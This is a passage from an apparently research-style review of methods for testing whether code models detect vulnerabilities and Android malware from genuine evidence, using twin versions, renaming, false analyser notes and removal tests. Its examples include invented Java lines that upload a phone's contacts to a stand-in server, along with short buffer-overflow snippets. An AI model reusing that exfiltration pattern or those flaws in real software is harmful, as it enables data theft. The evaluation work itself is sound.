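// Renamed original: the contacts leave the phone
List<T1> a = f1(ctx);
f2("files.example.net", f3(a));
```

The renamed version comes with a key because readers couldn't otherwise know that `f1` returns the address book, `f2` sends a file to a server and `f3` writes a list to a file. The table shows whether each reader reports stolen contacts, assuming this is one of the constant reader's stock claims.

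| Reader | Original | Twin | Renamed original | Renamed twin |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Correct answer | yes | no | yes | no |
| Constant reader | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| Name matcher | yes | yes | no | no |
| Data follower | yes | no | yes | no |

The twin exposes both the constant reader and the name matcher but doesn't distinguish them, because both raise the same false alarm. Renaming the original exposes the name matcher, which finds none of the names it matches on. The constant reader passes that test because it doesn't use names. The tester therefore needs both changes to identify all three readers.

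### Vulnerable–patched pairs

For vulnerabilities, the twins already exist, because a fix leaves behind one version of the function from before the change and one from after it. Ding, Fu and colleagues (2024), in *Vulnerability Detection with Code Language Models*, collected 5,480 such pairs as part of PrimeVul. They kept only pairs whose two versions share at least 80% of their text, so a model gets little help from length or coding style. The model judges each version separately, and the pair has one of four outcomes:

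- **Correct:** the model flags the vulnerable version and clears the patched one.
- **Both vulnerable:** it flags both versions.
- **Both benign:** it clears both versions.
- **Reversed:** it clears the vulnerable version and flags the patched one.

The reversed pairs give an idea of how many correct pairs are luck. A model that flags functions at random will, on average, produce as many reversed pairs as correct ones, whatever its flag rate. Recall equals the share of correct pairs plus the share of both-vulnerable pairs, and the false-alarm rate on patched code equals both-vulnerable plus reversed. Subtracting one from the other gives

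recall − false-alarm rate = correct − reversed

Ding and colleagues fine-tuned five open models on the older part of PrimeVul and tested them on 564 newer pairs. The figures are percentages of those pairs.

| Model | Correct | Both vulnerable | Both benign | Reversed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CodeT5 | 1.06 | 12.94 | 84.75 | 1.24 |
| CodeBERT | 1.77 | 11.35 | 86.17 | 0.71 |
| UniXcoder | 1.60 | 12.06 | 85.11 | 1.24 |
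| StarCoder2 | 2.30 | 8.16 | 88.30 | 1.24 |
| CodeGen2.5 | 3.01 | 10.82 | 84.22 | 1.95 |

StarCoder2's percentages correspond to 13 correct pairs and 7 reversed ones, which is hard to distinguish from chance. All five models were about 97% accurate on the full test set, but a program that always printed "safe" would have been more accurate than any of them, because 97.3% of the functions in that set were harmless.

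Risse and Böhme reached a similar conclusion in *Uncovering the Limits of Machine Learning for Automatic Vulnerability Detection* (2024). According to Liu and Gao's summary, the leading detectors had overfitted to features unrelated to the vulnerability and could not distinguish vulnerable functions from their patched versions. These findings are consistent with each other, because a feature unrelated to the vulnerability will usually remain after the patch.

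Newer models flag far more code but aren't much better at telling vulnerable versions from patched ones. GPT-5.2, for example, flagged both versions in most of Cichoń and Dmitruk's pairs. Liu and Gao ran DeepSeek's flash model on 187 PrimeVul pairs with and without step-by-step reasoning. Without it, the model flagged 45% of the vulnerable versions and, going by its overall flag rate, about 27% of the patched ones. With reasoning, the figures were 78% and about 60%. The gap was roughly 18 points both times, so reasoning led the model to flag more code without noticeably improving its ability to tell the versions apart.

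More guidance in the prompt didn't help much either. In a trial on 30 pairs, the version without reasoning enabled judged 10 correctly when the prompt asked it to work step by step. Adding facts from a program-analysis tool raised this to 11, while presenting the same facts as a checklist lowered it to 5 or 6. When Liu and Gao asked the model to reconsider its verdicts, it got 9 pairs right. It changed seven verdicts, and in five of them it wrongly flagged a patched function that it had correctly cleared before.

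Pairs also have weaknesses. The label "patched" refers to a single vulnerability, so if the function contains others, a model that flags it is right but is marked wrong. Fixes often add a check, so a model that treats any check as a sign of safety will get some pairs right without working out what the check protects. The evidence may also lie outside the function, as it did with `ingress_init`. *AEGIS* (2026) addresses this by cloning each project's repository at the exact commit and building a code graph from it.

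The way the tester presents the pair also matters. *TREAT* (2025) showed models both versions together and asked for a label for each, so a model could compare them and notice the added check. A model that sees one function at a time can't make that comparison. Scores from the two set-ups are therefore not comparable, even though the four outcomes have the same names in both.

A model may also judge a pair correctly from memory. When Ding and colleagues fine-tuned CodeGen2.5 on BigVul, an older dataset, it judged 40.84% of BigVul's test pairs correctly but only 1.24% of PrimeVul's. BigVul's usual split is random, so a model can train on the fixed version of a function and then be tested on the vulnerable one. About 12.7% of the vulnerable test functions were exact copies of training samples. Leakage probably explains part of the gap, although BigVul's labels are also less reliable. PrimeVul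 removes the copies and tests on the most recent code. This helps when testers fine-tune the model themselves, but a commercial model's original training data may already have included the fixes.

Malware has no fixing commits, so a tester has to write each twin by hand. The change should be as small as the one from `writeToFile(people)` to `crashLog`, and someone should confirm that the new version is harmless.

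### False notes about unchanged code

A model that copied its answers from accurate notes would pass both the twin test and the renaming test without looking at the code. This matters in practice because many systems give a model the output of a program-analysis tool along with the code. Liu and Gao studied what happens when that output is wrong, in a study covering 916 PrimeVul pairs, eleven model configurations from four vendors and 16,572 audits.

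They built an analyser that lists the risky operations in a function, such as array accesses. For each one it notes which conditions hold whenever the program gets there and what the function fails to guarantee. One of their examples comes from the gpac project, where the patched function contains this check, shown here in simplified form:

```c
if ((pps_id < 0) || (pps_id > 255))
    return -1;
```

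The vulnerable version doesn't rule out negative values of `pps_id`. A false assurance is a note added to that version claiming that line 12 checks `pps_id >= 0`, although line 12 contains only `return -1;`. A false alarm is a note claiming that a check present in the patched version is missing. A model can refute either note by reading the function.

Liu and Gao compared six conditions on their main set of 187 pairs (374 functions). Some conditions apply to only part of the set because there was not always a suitable analyser note to keep or falsify.

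| Notes given with the code | Content | Functions |
|---|---|---|
| None | The function only | 374 |
| All true | Everything the analyser reports | 374 |
| Relevant and true | Only notes on operations near the fix | 189 |
| Irrelevant and true | Only concerns about other operations | 183 |
| False assurance | Vulnerable version, with an invented guarantee | 83 |
| False alarm | Patched version, with an invented warning | 97 |

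Showing all the true notes raised accuracy by only two percentage points for the DeepSeek flash model, with or without reasoning, and both intervals included zero. Notes limited to the relevant operations helped slightly more, but not significantly.

To measure the effect of false notes, Liu and Gao compared them with true notes about the same operations, because even a true note might change the verdict by drawing the model's attention to a particular line.

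| Model | Vulnerable versions flagged: true notes → false assurances | Patched versions cleared: true notes → false alarms |
|---|---|---|
| deepseek-chat (flash, no reasoning) | 75% → 64% | 67% → 79% |
| deepseek-flash (with reasoning) | 87% → 90% | 37% → 55% |
| deepseek-v4-pro (with reasoning) | 97% → 83% | 29% → 32% |
| qwen-plus | 88% → 87% | 31% → 39% |

After reading the false assurances, deepseek-chat missed more vulnerabilities. Detection fell further for deepseek-v4-pro, but that result rests on only 29 functions and is not significant. False alarms had the opposite of their intended effect. The models looked at the line in question, found the supposedly missing check, and cleared the function more often than when a true note simply listed the check.

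Liu and Gao then ran seven more models. False assurances significantly lowered detection of vulnerable functions in four of them, by 19 points for GLM-5.2 and Kimi K3, 14 for Qwen3.7-flash and 13 for Qwen3.7-max. False alarms did not significantly lower accuracy in any of the eleven configurations.

Liu and Gao's main measure is how far verdicts move towards whatever the false note claims:

- assurance shift = share of "safe" verdicts with false assurances − share with true notes
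- alarm shift = share of "vulnerable" verdicts with false alarms − share with true notes
- asymmetry = assurance shift − alarm shift

For the first four configurations, the average was 0.03 − (−0.10) = 0.13. For the seven new models, it was 0.16, with an interval of 0.10 to 0.24. The second result is stronger because Liu and Gao wrote down their hypothesis and planned analysis before running those models, although no outside party recorded when they did so.

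The difference seems to come mostly from whether a model checks the claims it is given. By a conservative count, deepseek-chat disputed a false alarm in 80% of its answers and a false assurance in only 28%. When Liu and Gao asked it in a separate call to check every claim against the code, it refuted 79% of the false alarms and 76% of the false assurances. So it could usually identify a false assurance, but often accepted one when auditing the function. Difficulty may still explain some of the difference, since refuting an alarm means finding a check in the code, while refuting an assurance means establishing that there isn't one. On 57 pairs with both kinds of false note, the model refuted every false claim for 48 of the patched versions but only 36 of the vulnerable ones.

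Attempts to correct the problem had mixed results. Rewording each assurance as something "to verify" raised deepseek-chat's detection under false assurances from 64% to 82% on the main set. On 192 other pairs, the same wording raised detection only from 38% to 45%, which was not statistically significant. Liu and Gao chose the wording because it worked best on the main set, and they think this exaggerated its effect. Tuning a removal test and reporting its result on the same apps could easily exaggerate that result too.

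They next verified the claims in a separate call and showed the model which ones the code contradicted. They tested this once, on 300 unseen pairs. For deepseek-chat, detection under false assurances rose from 54% to 66% (p = 0.002), with no loss under true notes. For qwen-plus, detection rose from 78% to 84% under false assurances (p = 0.13) and fell by five points under true notes, but neither change was significant. On the development data, deleting the refuted claims had helped by 6 points, compared with 13 for showing them as refuted.

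However, a model that keeps its verdict may not have read the code. Kimi K2.6 flagged 79% of the functions even with true notes, and neither kind of false note changed its verdicts. A model that remembers the vulnerability from its training data could also ignore a false assurance without checking it. Liu and Gao point out that memorisation can't explain the differences between conditions, since the functions are the same in each. Memorisation therefore doesn't undermine their conclusion about models that changed their verdicts, but it could still explain why another model didn't. The study also used short C and C++ functions and made-up notes that the code plainly contradicts, so errors from a real tool may be harder to catch.

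A tester can adapt the method to malware by attaching a false note to the upload function, stating that it sends only crash logs. If the model then stops reporting stolen contacts, even though the upload code is still in the input, it based its judgement on the note. The comparison run needs a true note of similar length about the same function.

### New names for the same behaviour

Renaming tests whether a model makes the same judgement when the code's behaviour is unchanged but the names no longer reveal it. The tester replaces each name with a neutral one throughout the input, so that every call still refers to the right function, and compares evidence F1 before and after. The tester also has to make the same replacements in the expert report.

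The closest study on Android malware changed names in the opposite direction. *On Benchmarking Code LLMs for Android Malware Analysis* (He, She and colleagues, 2025) presented a framework called CAMA and tested it on 118 malware samples. Two of the four models, CodeLlama and StarChat, summarised the decompiled functions, suggested a better name for each one and rated its maliciousness from 0 to 10. A larger model supplied the ratings for the other two. The researchers then put CodeLlama's and StarChat's suggested names into the code and repeated the analysis.

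One of their measures is itself a removal test, although without a refill. A separate classifier reads the function summaries and names and predicts the malware category. The researchers remove the 2, 5 or 8 functions that the language model rated most malicious and calculate

relative drop = (confidence before − confidence after) / confidence before

Confidence here is the probability that the classifier assigns to its original category. The table shows the average relative drop in confidence with the decompiled names and with the model's suggested names.

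| Functions removed | CodeLlama: old → new names | StarChat: old → new names |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 0.158 → 0.485 | 0.111 → 0.298 |
| 5 | 0.159 → 0.451 | 0.254 → 0.351 |
| 8 | 0.113 → 0.440 | 0.275 → 0.726 |

New function names alone roughly tripled most of the drops. He and colleagues conclude that better names help the models pick out the malicious functions. In MalEval, the tested model also ranks its own evidence, so the same app could produce a quite different ΔS depending on how informative its function names are. But the classifier also reads text that the models wrote after the renaming, so the ranking may not account for the whole increase. Results also varied widely between apps. With the old names, CodeLlama's average drop after two removals was 0.158, with a standard deviation of 0.27.

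The malware descriptions scored lower on METEOR, a measure of how closely a text matches a reference, with a fall of 11% for CodeLlama and 10% for StarChat. He et al. suggest that the new names pushed more maliciousness scores towards the middle of the scale, so the highest-ranked functions stood out less.

CAMA's experiment shows that names matter, but not that the models fail without them. Decompiled names are often meaningless, and the model based its suggested names on its own reading of each function. To test whether a model matches names, the tester has to remove informative names.

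Liu, Han and colleagues (2026), in *DiagChain*, did replace informative names, though in attack logs rather than code. In their benchmark, a model must reconstruct the steps of an attack from log records and cite the records that support each step. In a side experiment on 15 publicly documented cases, they replaced identifiers such as CVE numbers, host names, IP addresses, domains and file paths with substitutes of the same type. They used the same substitute for an identifier everywhere it appeared, including in the reference answer. An automated check found none of the original names left.

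Four of the five models then scored between 53% and 60% on structural F1, a score for the reconstructed attack that the researchers report only for this side experiment. Llama2-7B, a much older model, scored 16.9%. The other four could evidently reconstruct a good part of an attack without the original names, so for that part they did not need any memory that depends on recognising a particular server or CVE number.

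Liu, Han and colleagues did not run the same 15 cases with the original names under the same settings. A score of 55% could therefore mean that renaming had no effect or that it lowered the score by 20 points. Their main experiments did use the original names, but allowed the model up to 15 rounds of investigation instead of eight. They acknowledge that they can't estimate the effect of renaming or rule out contamination from training data.

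Even with a matched run, a drop after renaming would not necessarily mean that the model was using a shortcut. Function names can be legitimate evidence, and an analyst without them would also be less accurate. Neutral names also make ordinary code look like the output of an obfuscator, which malware authors often use, so the tester should rename harmless apps too and check whether the model starts flagging them. Renaming may change little in the MalEval samples whose authors have already scrambled the names.

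If the tester renames one of Android's own functions, such as `readContacts`, to `f1` without defining it, a model that follows the data fails for the same reason as one that matches names. The key in the opening example solves this, but a model could match words in the key instead. The renamed twin helps detect this, because its key mentions both the address book and the server even though no contacts leave the phone.

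### Running the model with no evidence

The no-code run provides a floor for measuring the drop. It can also test whether the model relies on memory, if the prompt contains something the model could remember.

DiagChain shows why that condition matters, because its models needed the logs to complete the task. In the same side experiment, Liu, Han and colleagues gave the five models only a minimal, anonymous brief, with no log records and no way to search for any. Every model scored zero on structural F1. Four returned no attack steps in any of the 15 cases, and Qwen2.5-7B returned some in about a quarter of the cases, but none were correct. All five models did better with the renamed evidence available, and the intervals for the improvement excluded zero.

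This doesn't show that the models had no memory of the attacks. The brief did not identify the incident, so even a model trained on a full account of it would have had no way to pick out that account. The benchmark's main prompt may also have encouraged empty answers, because it tells models to leave out any claim the evidence does not support, and a model that follows it should return nothing when there is no evidence.

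*The SWE-Bench Illusion* (2025) asked models to name the faulty files in a software project from a description of the bug, without seeing the repository. A specific bug gives a model something to recognise, and a file path is easy to mark right or wrong. A correct path may not come from memory, however, because the description may contain the file's name or make it easy to guess. The tester can check the description for such clues and compare the results with those for bugs reported after the model's training ended. If the model names the right file much more often for old bugs than for new ones of similar difficulty, memory is a likely reason.

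For the Maikspy example, the equivalent would take three runs without any code:

1. An anonymous prompt asks for a malware report on an unspecified Android app. This estimates the score from stock claims, as in the ordinary no-code run.
2. The same prompt says that the app belongs to the Maikspy family.
3. The same prompt gives an invented family name that sounds equally suspicious.

The constant reader writes the same report for all three prompts. A model that remembers published findings should score higher with the family's real name than with either of the other prompts. The invented name is a control, because a word like "spy" could lead to better guesses without any memory of the family. If the code contains a server address or another recognisable string, the tester should try that string in place of the family name, since it may be what triggers the memory during a normal audit.

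A high score with the real name shows that the model knows the family, but not that it relies on this knowledge when it has the code. The tester can check by restoring the code with one fact changed, such as having the upload function send the call log instead of contacts. A model that still reports stolen contacts from that function is probably repeating what it remembers about Maikspy, or what it expects of spyware in general. Making the same change in an app from an unknown family would help separate the two explanations.

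## Removal tests on vulnerability and malware detectors

Security researchers were removing evidence from detectors' inputs years before MalEval. The early tests checked the explanations of a detector's decisions rather than the detector itself. A tool listed the features behind a decision, and the researchers deleted those features to see whether the decision changed.

### Removing features to check an explanation

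LEMNA, a method from 2018, explains a classifier's decisions one at a time. It makes about 500 altered copies of the input, records the classifier's output for each, and fits a simpler model that shows which features mattered. Its developers tried it on two classifiers. One finds where functions begin in compiled programs, from sequences of up to 200 bytes. The other recognises malicious PDF files from 135 features, such as whether the file contains JavaScript.

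The LEMNA paper tested explanations by blanking the features that LEMNA ranked highest and counting how many inputs kept their original label. In the function finder, blanking five bytes left at most 25% of the labels unchanged, and blanking 35 left almost none. The paper also tested copying the top features of one input into an input of the opposite class. In the PDF classifier, copying five features changed the label in 75% of cases. LEMNA beat a random choice of features in all the tests, whereas LIME did no better than random on the PDF classifier.

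These are good results for LEMNA, but they say little about whether the classifiers use sound evidence. A harmless PDF doesn't become malware because five of its features match those of a malicious one, so the 75% is, if anything, a bad sign for the classifier. The function finder raises a similar question with byte sequences like this one:

```
90 90 90 90 83 ec 4c
```

The function starts at `83`. Each `90` is an instruction that does nothing, which compilers often insert as padding before a function. LEMNA showed that the classifier was using this padding, and LEMNA's developers counted that as a well-known and reasonable rule. But the padding would be missing from code compiled without it, so relying on it could equally be called a shortcut. Blanking the padding causes a large drop whether the classifier's use of it is considered a reasonable rule or a shortcut.

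Descriptive accuracy, a measure from 2020, turned the same idea into a score:

DA(k) = p(original answer | input with its k most relevant features set to zero)

Suppose a detector gives "vulnerable" a probability of 0.97, which falls to 0.22 when the ten top-ranked features are removed. DA(10) is then 0.22, and a lower value means a better explanation. The drop of 0.75 is what *ERASER* calls comprehensiveness.

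The paper that introduced the measure compared six explanation methods on four detectors, two for Android malware, one for malicious PDFs and one for vulnerabilities. Results differed significantly between the methods, and these differences must come from the rankings because the detectors stayed the same. A high value of the measure, like a small ΔS, can mean either that the ranking is poor or that the detector ignores its input.

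### Shrinking a function until only the essentials remain

Suneja and colleagues added the missing check in their 2020 study. They removed as much code as they could while the model still answered "vulnerable", then looked for the original bug in what was left. Their method, input minimisation, uses delta debugging, a technique that programmers first used to shorten bug reports for the Mozilla browser. It works like this:

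1. Take a function that the model correctly calls vulnerable, and split its tokens into two parts.
2. Try each part by itself, then the whole function without each part.
3. Accept a shorter version only if it compiles, the model still calls it vulnerable, and a checker finds either the original bug or no bug at all. The last condition stops the shrinking from introducing new bugs.
4. Continue from an accepted version. If there isn't one, split the code into twice as many parts and try again.
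5. Stop when removing any single token would break one of the conditions.
6. Ask the checker whether the final version still contains the original bug.

Here is one of their short examples:

```c
void foo(int a) { int b = 10; int buf[10]; a + 3; buf[b] = 1; }
```

The array has slots 0 to 9, so writing to slot 10 overflows it. Neither halves nor quarters of this function compile. With eight parts, the search finds that it can drop `a + 3;`, which does nothing:

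```c
void foo(int a) { int b = 10; int buf[10]; buf[b] = 1; }
```

The model still called this version vulnerable. The search removed a few more tokens and stopped at the 46th version, which still contained the overflow, so the model got credit for the detection.

Another model did worse on a function from the Juliet test suite. The relevant lines, slightly simplified, copy too many characters into an array with ten slots:

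```c
wchar_t *data = new wchar_t[10];
wchar_t source[10+1] = SRC_STRING;
size_t sourceLen = wcslen(source);
for (size_t i = 0; i < sourceLen + 1; i++) {
    data[i] = source[i];
}
printWLine(data);
```

After shrinking, this remained:

```c
wchar_t *data = new wchar_t[10];
wchar_t source[10+1] = SRC_STRING;
size_t i = wcslen(source);
for (;;) { }
(data);
```

The code no longer writes to `data`, so the overflow is gone, but the model still classified the code as vulnerable. Its F1 score on Juliet was 97 out of 100.

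### Signal-aware recall

Signal-aware recall counts a detection only if the bug survives the shrinking:

signal-aware recall = detections whose shrunken version still has the original bug / all vulnerable functions

If a test set has 100 vulnerable functions, a model flags 96 of them, and the bug survives in 58, recall is 96% and signal-aware recall is 58%. Suneja and colleagues calculated both for three kinds of neural network on three datasets:

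| Dataset | Network | Recall (%) | Signal-aware recall (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| s-bAbI | Convolutional | 95.4 | 58.4 |
| s-bAbI | Recurrent | 95.9 | 59.6 |
| s-bAbI | Graph | 99.7 | 62.7 |
| Juliet | Convolutional | 99.9 | 77.0 |
| Juliet | Recurrent | 98.6 | 76.0 |
| Juliet | Graph | 99.9 | 76.8 |
| GitHub | Convolutional | 54.9 | 46.2 |
| GitHub | Recurrent | 61.8 | 52.4 |
| GitHub | Graph | 69.8 | 60.8 |

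The study's headline result, a fall in recall from the high 90s to about 60%, applies only to s-bAbI, a set of computer-generated programs whose only flaws are buffer overflows. On Juliet, recall fell to 76–77%. On real functions from five GitHub projects, the models lost 13 to 16% of their detections, compared with 37 to 39% on s-bAbI.

These results don't show that the models understood real code best, because they were only 57 to 60% accurate on the GitHub functions and about 12 to 13% of their detections there couldn't be shortened at all. For the convolutional network, this was always because the code didn't compile. These detections presumably count in the model's favour, since a function that never shrank still has its bug.

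The three networks' detections that passed the bug check also overlapped by 91% on s-bAbI and 96.9% on Juliet, but only 49.3% on GitHub. Because one network reads code as a kind of image, one as a sequence and one as a graph, Suneja and colleagues suspect that all three had learned the same quirks of the artificial datasets. The overlap on s-bAbI is more striking than on Juliet because each network passed the check on only about 60% of the s-bAbI functions, and independent successes would overlap far less.

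### What the bug check can and can't tell

Input minimisation easily catches a constant reader, because the functions it flags shrink to almost nothing and the bugs disappear. It can also catch a name matcher, which ordinary removal could not distinguish from a data follower. Suppose someone adapts the method to spyware and starts from this invented code:

```java
List<Contact> people = readContacts(ctx);
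File dump = crashLog;
dump = writeToFile(people);
ftp.upload("files.example.net", dump);
```

If the search deletes the third line, the program uploads only the crash log. The name matcher still reports stolen contacts because both suspicious calls remain, so it gets no credit. The data follower changes its answer, so the search has to put the line back.

But the result depends on the order of the deletions. If the search deletes `= crashLog` first, the third line has to stay, because Java won't compile a program that uses `dump` before giving it a value. The final version then still steals contacts, so the test wrongly counts the name matcher as having detected the theft. Suneja and colleagues acknowledge that the search may miss a smaller version without the bug, so they call signal-aware recall an upper bound.

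Duplicated evidence can instead make the score too low. Suppose either the overflow or some quirk of the dataset is enough for a "vulnerable" answer. The search can then delete the overflow, and the model loses credit even though it would have found the bug without the quirk. A bug missing from the shrunken code shows that the model didn't need it, but not that the model ignored it in the original. The shrunken code can also look strange, like the empty endless loop above, and some answers may be reactions to that.

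A model unfairly loses credit if the checker misses a bug that is still there, and unfairly gains credit if the checker reports one that is gone. Suneja and colleagues mostly used Infer, a program-analysis tool, and compared line numbers where Infer disagreed with the dataset's label. Infer suited the GitHub dataset unusually well because its creators had started from Infer's warnings. The researchers still found a similar problem when they used line matching alone, which is more generous to the models. For malware, the tester would need a checker that can detect whether a shrunken app still steals contacts.

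In a follow-up paper, *Data-Driven and SE-assisted AI Model Signal-Awareness Enhancement and Introspection*, Suneja, Zhuang and colleagues (2021) tried to improve the scores through training. Showing the models simple functions before complex ones raised signal awareness by up to 32%. Adding shrunken programs to the training data, labelled by whether they still contained the bug, raised it to as much as 4.8 times its previous level. Since a score can't exceed 100%, the largest gain must have started from below 21%, lower than any score in the table.

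Training on the shrunken programs probably helps in two ways. The model learns that code without the bug is safe, as intended. The test inputs also become familiar to it, much as they did when Hase and colleagues trained on text with missing tokens. The higher score doesn't show how much each effect contributed.

### Taking away the context around a function

Studies of language models in 2026 have removed whole categories of input instead of single tokens. Armillotta, Romandini and colleagues (2026), in *Antaeus*, looked for logic vulnerabilities, where the code does what it says but lacks a check that the project's own rules require. One example comes from libvirt, a library for managing virtual machines. In outline:

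```c
int virDomainAgentSetResponseTimeout(domain, timeout, flags) {
    conn = domain->conn;
    /* no check for read-only callers */
    return conn->driver->domainAgentSetResponseTimeout(domain, timeout, flags);
}
```

A user with read-only access can set the timeout to zero and disrupt the service. The function contains no sign that read-only users exist, so a reader has to learn this from the rest of the project.

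Antaeus, a system by Armillotta and colleagues, gives the model two kinds of context. Local context contains the functions the code calls and the macros, constants and types it uses. Repository context is a summary of the whole project, including its purpose, users and what it has to protect. A language model writes the summary and links it to excerpts from the code. Armillotta and colleagues tested the system on 35 projects, each with one known vulnerability, and counted a detection only if the model also explained the flaw correctly.

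| Input | Found by Opus 4.7 | Found by GPT-5.4 |
|---|---|---|
| Function with both kinds of context | 20 | 14 |
| Without local context | 13 | 9 |
| Without repository context | 11 | 8 |
| Function only (separate baseline) | 9 | 8 |

They give no intervals for these figures, but their results for individual vulnerabilities allow a rough check. Without local context, Opus missed seven vulnerabilities that it found when that context was included, and it found no new ones. An exact McNemar test gives p ≈ 0.016. Without repository context, it missed nine and found no new ones (p ≈ 0.004).

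The real effect may be smaller, because the 20 includes every vulnerability that Opus found in at least one of three runs, while an average run found about 17. The number of runs without context is not reported, but if those results are from single runs, 17 is the fairer comparison. Of the 14 vulnerabilities that Opus found in all three full runs, it still found 12 without local context and 10 without repository context. Most of the missed vulnerabilities were therefore ones that the full system found in only some runs, although four of the nine missed without repository context were ones it had found in all three.

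Armillotta and colleagues do not describe replacing the removed text with anything, so the prompts also became shorter. The complete system used about 101 million input tokens with Opus, while the function-only baseline used under 7 million. Replacing the repository summary with one of equal length from an unrelated project would show how much the content mattered.

A model may detect a flaw without relying on the code it was given, as the libvirt results suggest. Opus found the flaw in the libvirt function only with repository context, as the researchers expected. But GPT-5.4 found it in all three runs of the function-only baseline, which included no information about read-only users. It may have drawn on training data about the flaw, which has been public since 2020, or about how libvirt normally handles such users. It may also have flagged the flaw by chance, since it reported about 44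 false findings in the same project.

Memory is unlikely to explain the results as a whole. Seven of the vulnerabilities became public after the models' training data ended, and the full system with Opus found four of them (57%). It found 16 of the 28 older ones (also 57%). Seven cases are too few to rule out a moderate advantage from memory, but they show that the system can work without it.

### Taking away the fields that rules use

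In *MARS*, Choi (2026) removed evidence from Windows and Linux programs to compare three ways of judging them. All three start from the same evidence, including imported functions, text strings, web addresses and file properties. In direct classification, a language model reads the evidence and gives a verdict. In single-pass processing, the model lists claims about the program, and a fixed formula turns them into a verdict. The third method uses fixed rules and no language model.

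The formula for single-pass processing gives each claim a weight for its category and multiplies it by a factor for its severity:

score = sum of (category weight × severity factor)

Suppose a model makes three claims of medium severity, which has a factor of 1. Suspicious function calls have a weight of 2.2, commands 1.8 and network indicators 1.0, so the score is 5.0. With GLM-5.2, a program needs a score of at least 3.025 to raise an alert, so this one does. If the evidence for the commands and network indicators disappears, the score falls to 2.2 and the program no longer raises an alert, even though the suspicious calls are still there.

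Choi took 182 files, half of them malicious, removed the fields that the fixed rules use, and compared the results with a new run on the full evidence. The figures for the two language-model methods combine results from Gemini 2.5 Flash, Gemma4-31B and GLM-5.2. Recall is the share of malicious programs that trigger an alert.

| Method | Change in recall (points) | 95% interval |
|---|---|---|
| Rules alone | −34.1 | −43.9 to −24.4 |
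| Single-pass processing | −29.2 | −36.1 to −22.1 |
| Direct classification | −10.0 | −14.6 to −5.5 |

The rules started with a recall of 34.1%, so they lost all of it. This was inevitable, because Choi chose to remove the fields that the rules depend on, but it confirms that the removal worked. Choi's alert counts imply that single-pass processing started at about 67%, so it lost more than two fifths of its recall. Direct classification lost far less. The same three models averaged about 90% with this method on the full collection of 1,195 programs, so a 10-point drop is roughly a ninth of its recall.

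Random variation probably didn't cause the 10-point drop, because 98.0% of the alert decisions stayed the same when Choi reran direct classification on unchanged malicious programs. The cause of the larger drop in single-pass processing is less clear. A fixed threshold, as in the GLM-5.2 example, could turn a partial loss of evidence into a missed alert, but the experiment doesn't separate the effects of the claims, their categories and the formula.

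Choi doesn't describe a refill either, but two of his other experiments suggest how one might affect the results. Adding harmless-looking material to malicious programs lowered the recall of direct classification by 4.4 points (interval 1.5 to 8.1), although no evidence was missing. Adding a large amount of unrelated material had no clear effect on recall, but the share of harmless programs that direct classification labelled benign fell by 5.5 to 11.0 points, depending on the model. Effects of that size could cancel out or produce much of a 10-point drop.

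Evidence removed from one place can easily survive in another. In another experiment, Choi trained a simple text classifier to identify malware families from the evidence. Removing the fields for web addresses and domains barely changed its accuracy, which went from 59.7% to 58.0% on Windows programs and from 82.1% to 82.8% on Linux programs. With the text strings alone, the classifier still reached 56.0% and 80.7%. Choi notes that identifying details may have remained in the strings, and the same could be true of the fields in the main removal test.

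### Reliance on code or on priors

Direct classification's loss in MARS may be small because the model can still work out what a program does from its imported functions, without the obvious indicators. But another model could lose the same 10 points because it treats packed, unsigned files as malicious, and those properties are still in the input.

Such shortcuts were available. Choi trained a classifier on only the processor type, file size, randomness of the bytes, packing and signature. Its balanced accuracy, the average of its accuracy on malicious and harmless programs, was 93.6% for Windows programs. The six language models averaged 92.4% with direct classification. Choi balanced the 182 files so that processor type did not indicate whether a file was malicious, but the other cues remained. The trained classifier shows how accurate a model can be using only these cues, but not whether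 the language models used them.

A large loss wouldn't prove that the model reads the code carefully either. The rules assign scores to matches with YARA patterns, which analysts write to recognise known malware. A model that detects much less malware without those matches may have been repeating another tool's verdict.

Antaeus always keeps the function under examination in the input, so the test measures what the context adds. Context may help a model understand the function, or it may only suggest a standard flaw to report. For example, a model told that libvirt has read-only users could report a missing read-only check in every function that changes a setting, and it would sometimes be right. Running the patched function with the same context would help distinguish these two effects.

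Both studies also lack a run with no evidence and a run with random parts removed. The function-only baseline is the closest to a no-evidence run, but it still contains the code that the model has to judge.

MalEval is the only design in this table that refills the input:

| Design | What the researchers removed | Refill | Comparison | What the result supports |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LEMNA's removal test | Top-ranked features | No, blanked | Random features and LIME | Whether the ranking finds features that the classifier uses |
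| Descriptive accuracy | The k top-ranked features | No, set to zero | Other explanation methods | Which method ranks features better |
| Input minimisation | Everything the model doesn't need for a "vulnerable" answer | No | A check for the original bug | Whether the model needs the bug |
| Antaeus | Local or repository context | None described | Full context, and the function alone | Whether context helps the model find logic vulnerabilities |
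| MARS | Fields that the fixed rules use | None described | A new run on the full evidence, and rules alone | How much each method depends on those fields |
| MalEval | Top-ranked function summaries | Yes, with lower-ranked summaries | The full input | Whether the top-ranked functions affect the evidence score |
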